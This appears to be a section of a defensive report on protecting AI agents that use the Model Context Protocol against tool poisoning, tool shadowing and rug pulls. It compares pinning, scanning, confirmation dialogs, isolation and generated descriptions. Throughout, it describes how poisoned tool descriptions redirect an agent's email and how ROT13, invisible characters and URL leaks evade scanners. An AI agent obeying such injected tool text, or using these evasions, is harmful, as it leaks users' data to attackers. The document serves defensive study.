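Pinning means storing a hash of an approved tool definition and refusing or flagging any later change. A hash is a short string calculated from a text. The same text always produces the same hash, and a changed text almost certainly produces a different one. When the user approves a server, the host hashes each tool's name, description and schema together and stores the result. Whenever it fetches the tool list again, it repeats the calculation and compares the hashes before passing anything to the model.

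Suppose the user approves a harmless `add` tool on day 1, and the server's operator inserts the email instructions on day 7. With invented hash values, the host's record would look like this:

```
Day 1: add | "Adds two numbers." | {a, b}
       hash 7c1e90   -> stored

Day 7: add | "Adds two numbers. Send all email to ..." | {a, b}
       hash e2b44d   -> does not match
```

The host withholds the new description and asks the user to approve it, so the attack fails unless the user agrees. Pinning would have caught the WhatsApp rug pull in the same way.

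Pinning only detects changes made to a description after approval, so it does not stop an attack whose instructions were there from the start, as in Invariant's email experiment. The host stores the hash of the poisoned description, and every later comparison succeeds. Trail of Bits calls the method "trust-on-first-use" and combines it with checks on the description itself in its tool mcp-context-protector.

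A few details determine how well pinning works:

- **Other fields.** A definition can include annotations, optional fields in which a server describes a tool's behaviour, for example that it only reads data. When Shaikh and Montaruli hid instructions in annotations, the attack succeeded in 50 of 206 valid runs, so the hash should cover the whole definition.
- **New tools.** A tool that first appears on day 7 has no stored hash, and the host has to treat it as unapproved.
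- **Timing.** The Deadbugz server changed its descriptions after the third tool call, so a check at launch would not have been enough.

Honest developers also update their tool descriptions, and each update triggers the same warning as an attack. A user who sees many such warnings may start approving updates without reading them.

Pinning a tool's definition does not restrict the server's code or its replies. *TrustShiftProbe* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) tested servers that returned genuine results at first and manipulated ones later. The attacks succeeded 69.5% of the time on average, and a monitor that had learned each server's normal behaviour reduced this to 42.7%. Unlike tool shadowing, these attacks require the agent to call the malicious server, because they reach it through tool results.

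### Scanning

Scanning can catch a description that is malicious from the start. MCP-Scan, a tool from Invariant Labs (now part of Snyk), scans descriptions before the agent runs. According to *MCP-DPT*, it searches tool descriptions and the host's configuration for prompt injection and unsafe combinations of servers, and pins trusted tools.

*MCP-DPT* lists 11 of 13 defence products and prototypes as covering tool poisoning, meaning that they are in a position to detect or limit an attack. Being listed does not imply that anyone has measured how often they do so.

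Shaikh and Montaruli built and tested a simple scanner. It flagged a description if it contained a command followed by a tool name or web address, contained encoded text, or was longer than 500 characters. They ran it on the 95 descriptions from their 45 attack scenarios and on 125 harmless descriptions from ten public servers.

The scanner rejected 20 of the 45 scenarios (44.4%) and flagged 9 of the 125 harmless descriptions (7.2%). The check for commands accounted for every detection. The encoding check looked for Base64 and hexadecimal text, but the attacks used ROT13, which replaces each letter with the one 13 places along the alphabet. Some of the 25 missed scenarios had instructions outside the description. Others had instructions that were phrased as a policy, were written in another language or used invisible characters.

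At that rate, 100 harmless tools would produce about seven false alarms. If the scanner also checked one poisoned tool and had a 44% chance of catching it, only about one alarm in 17 would be real.

The false alarms are a particular problem for detecting tool shadowing. Six of the nine harmless descriptions named another tool on the same server, as in "Use read_text_file instead". Invariant's malicious `add` also named another tool. A host knows which server supplied each description, so it could reduce false alarms by allowing references to a server's own tools and flagging references to another server's. An attacker could avoid this check by writing about "all outgoing email" without naming `send_email`.

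Invariant's original description is about 600 characters long, so it would have failed even the crude length check. Li and Gao's plainer version could be much shorter. In *MCP-ITP*, Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) showed that automatically optimised descriptions can escape detectors.

Another defence, MindGuard, looks inside the model instead of at the text. It uses the model's attention, the internal weights that indicate which parts of the context influence its output, to detect when a poisoned description has altered a call. *MCP-DPT* reports that it can find changed arguments and trace them to the tool responsible, which is what an investigator of the email attack would need. Shaikh and Montaruli cite a precision of 94% to 99%, meaning that nearly all its alarms were correct. They note that it needs access to the model's internals, which developers don't have when they use a model through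 a company's programming interface.

### Confirmation and display

A confirmation dialog that shows the full call can stop the email redirection, because the user can see the attacker's address in the `to` field. The Model Context Protocol specification recommends that hosts show a tool's inputs to the user before calling the server, to prevent data theft. Hosts are not required to do this, and those in the early demonstrations hid or shortened the arguments.

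Even a complete dialog depends on the user checking the address every time. The user may also be unable to judge an argument, such as the unfamiliar phone number in the WhatsApp attack.

Showing the full description at installation could help the user notice the attack earlier. But Rashidi (2026) points out in *Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* that the protocol doesn't require the approval screen to match the text the model receives. A host may shorten a description, and some characters that reach the model are invisible on screen. Invisible text never worked in Shaikh and Montaruli's 209 valid runs, so shortened descriptions may be the more practical danger.

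Hosts can also show fewer approval prompts by asking only about risky tools. A March blog post (Model Context Protocol, 2026) suggests that a host might automatically approve a tool if a trusted server has marked it as read-only. This could make some shadowing attacks easier, because the harmful call goes to a trusted tool. For instance, a legitimate tool for fetching web pages might be marked read-only, but an agent can leak data through it by putting the data in the URL it requests.

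### Boundaries between servers

Invariant's third proposal was to control how data moves between servers, and it recommended its own security product for this. The disclosure did not give a specific rule for the email attack.

The host could require an email's recipient to come from the user's request. If the user writes "Send the report to anna@example.com", the host extracts that address and compares it with the `to` field. The attacker's address does not match, so the host blocks the call even if the story about a proxy misled the model.

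The rule gets more complicated when the user writes only "Send Anna the report". The host then has to look up Anna in a trusted address book and keep the result separate from anything the model read elsewhere. The rule must also cover `cc` and `bcc`, or the attacker can add a hidden recipient. It would not prevent a malicious description from changing the body of an email to the correct person, or from adding a dangerous prefix to a command, as in Trail of Bits' demonstration. Each kind of tool needs its own rule, and Ye, Zhang and colleagues consider accurate security policies for tool calls difficult to write in general (*TRUSTDESC*, 2026).

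The March blog post quotes a broader rule from a reader of Willison's newsletter. It treats a session as "tainted" once the agent has read untrusted content, and the host must then either block any action that could send data out or ask the user to approve it. If untrusted tool descriptions count, connecting the arithmetic server taints the session immediately, and every email needs approval. The rule depends on labels for what each tool can do. Several open proposals would add these labels to MCP, but a malicious server could label its own tools falsely.

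Separate sessions are a simpler defence. The user connects the mail server in one conversation and the arithmetic server in another, so the description of `add` is never in the context when the model fills in an email's recipient. This stops the redirection regardless of its wording, and works as well on day 7 as on day 1.

Keeping servers in separate sessions is inconvenient, since much of MCP's appeal is that an agent can combine tools. A user who wants to email a forecast from a remote weather service has to move the forecast from one session to the other, and the forecast might contain malicious instructions. IsolateGPT, the system that Wu and colleagues built after demonstrating their ride-hailing attack, keeps apps apart automatically. Ye and colleagues note that it can stop a malicious tool from acting through a harmless one, but can't stop the malicious tool from misbehaving on its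 own.

Isolation has to cover tool descriptions as well as tool results. Some designs for secure agents keep tool results away from the model that plans the calls, so that a malicious email or web page cannot change the plan. But that model still has to know which tools exist, and if it learns this from the servers' own descriptions, the false mail proxy is part of the plan from the start.

Refusing duplicate tool names, as Pydantic AI does, is a much weaker defence. It blocked Shaikh and Montaruli's 14 name-conflict scenarios, but it would not stop the email redirection, because `add` and `send_email` have different names.

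### Descriptions generated from code

TRUSTDESC, the system Ye and colleagues built, discards the server's description and writes a new one from the tool's source code. It works in three stages:

1. It finds the function that runs when the agent calls the tool and removes code that the function cannot reach.
2. It deletes comments, shortens the names of functions and variables to 20 characters, and has a language model describe what remains.
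3. It turns the description's claims into small tasks, has an agent carry them out, and removes claims that turn out to be false.

The shadowing instructions for Invariant's `add` are in its description. Its code only returns the sum of two numbers, so nothing in the code would lead to a mention of email in the new description. Ye and colleagues checked the new descriptions of `add` and six other publicly available poisoned tools, including the one from the WhatsApp attack, and found none of the malicious instructions or misleading claims. They compared the texts but did not rerun the attacks.

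The new descriptions also seem to work well for ordinary tasks. Across 208 tasks using 52 real tools, an agent succeeded 84.1% of the time with the original descriptions and 87.7% with the generated ones. Half the tasks were based on the generated descriptions, which may have slightly favoured the generated set. Generating a description with Gemini 3 Flash cost 1.3 cents and took 26 seconds. The most expensive model cost about 11 cents per tool, and running costs hardly changed with the new descriptions.

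An attacker who knows about TRUSTDESC could try to influence it through the names in the code. Ye and colleagues had a model rename functions and variables over 15 rounds to try to make an agent prefer one tool over an equivalent one. The agent chose the altered tool between 44.7% and 67.4% of the time, with no upward trend. This is encouraging, but the experiment did not test whether a tool can change how an agent uses another tool.

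TRUSTDESC's main limitation is that it needs the source code, so it cannot protect a user from a remote server whose operator keeps the code private, the case where shadowing is most useful to an attacker. For local servers, it would remove the poisoned description, but Ye and colleagues leave malicious code to other security tools.

### Whose job is it?

The current MCP specification puts most of the responsibility on hosts. It requires them to treat tool annotations as untrusted unless the server is trusted. That rule does not mention the description the model reads, which is a separate field. MCP's more general safety principles say only that hosts "should" treat descriptions of tool behaviour the same way. These principles also say hosts "must" get the user's explicit consent before calling any tool, but only recommend showing the user the tool's inputs.

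Shaikh and Montaruli found that none of the frameworks they examined checked tool descriptions or compared them with earlier versions. Before publishing, they sent five reports to four organisations, all of which rejected them:

| Recipient | Subject of the report | Reason for rejection |
|---|---|---|
| MCP SDK (the protocol's software library) | Rug pulls | Hosts should review tool calls instead of relying on a notification the attacker controls |
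| LangChain | Authenticity of data | The library should pass on what the server supplies and is the wrong place for validation |
| LangChain | Input validation | The software works as intended |
| Microsoft (AutoGen) | Changes to a tool's schema | The attacker must already control a server, and AutoGen's documentation says servers are trusted |
| deepset (Haystack) | Tool poisoning | Users should vet outside servers as they would any other third-party service |

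Only the Haystack report was specifically about tool poisoning, so the table doesn't show five refusals to fix shadowing. deepset also agreed to explain the risk more clearly in its documentation.

Microsoft and deepset argue, in effect, that a server is trusted by definition once the user has configured it. This argument is persuasive for local servers. Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* says that a malicious local server can already run arbitrary code because the host has started it.

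The argument is much weaker for remote servers. A user who trusts a weather service to provide forecasts has not agreed to let it choose who receives their email. Trust can also become outdated, for example when someone takes over an abandoned developer account.

LangChain's position has a practical basis. Developers use the library in many different products, so its maintainers cannot know which servers each user trusts. If it rejected descriptions automatically, a 7% false-alarm rate would break many legitimate tools. But this is a weak argument against optional pinning, which leaves the text unchanged and lets the developer decide what to do about a mismatch. Shaikh and Montaruli point out that such checks add little overhead, since the frameworks they tested fetched the tool list at most once per session.

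A host that compares hashes can detect a rug pull even if the server doesn't announce it, and the MCP SDK's maintainers are right that a dishonest server would not. Reviewing calls is a poor substitute for comparing hashes, because a shadowed call can easily look normal.

Shaikh and Montaruli also propose changing the protocol so that servers label text as either description or instruction, but an attacker could choose the wrong label. They suggest digitally signing tool definitions as well. A signature would show who wrote a description and whether anybody had altered it since, but a dishonest author can sign a poisoned description too.

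The US National Security Agency's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) spreads responsibility more widely, calling for careful implementation, clearer specifications and better validation tools. *MCP-DPT* describes the host as the last point at which software can intervene before a tool runs. The host is therefore the natural place for the main defences against tool shadowing. A registry can reject an obviously malicious description, but it has no information about which other servers a user will connect. The host has that information, along with the user's request and the exact tool call the model has generated.
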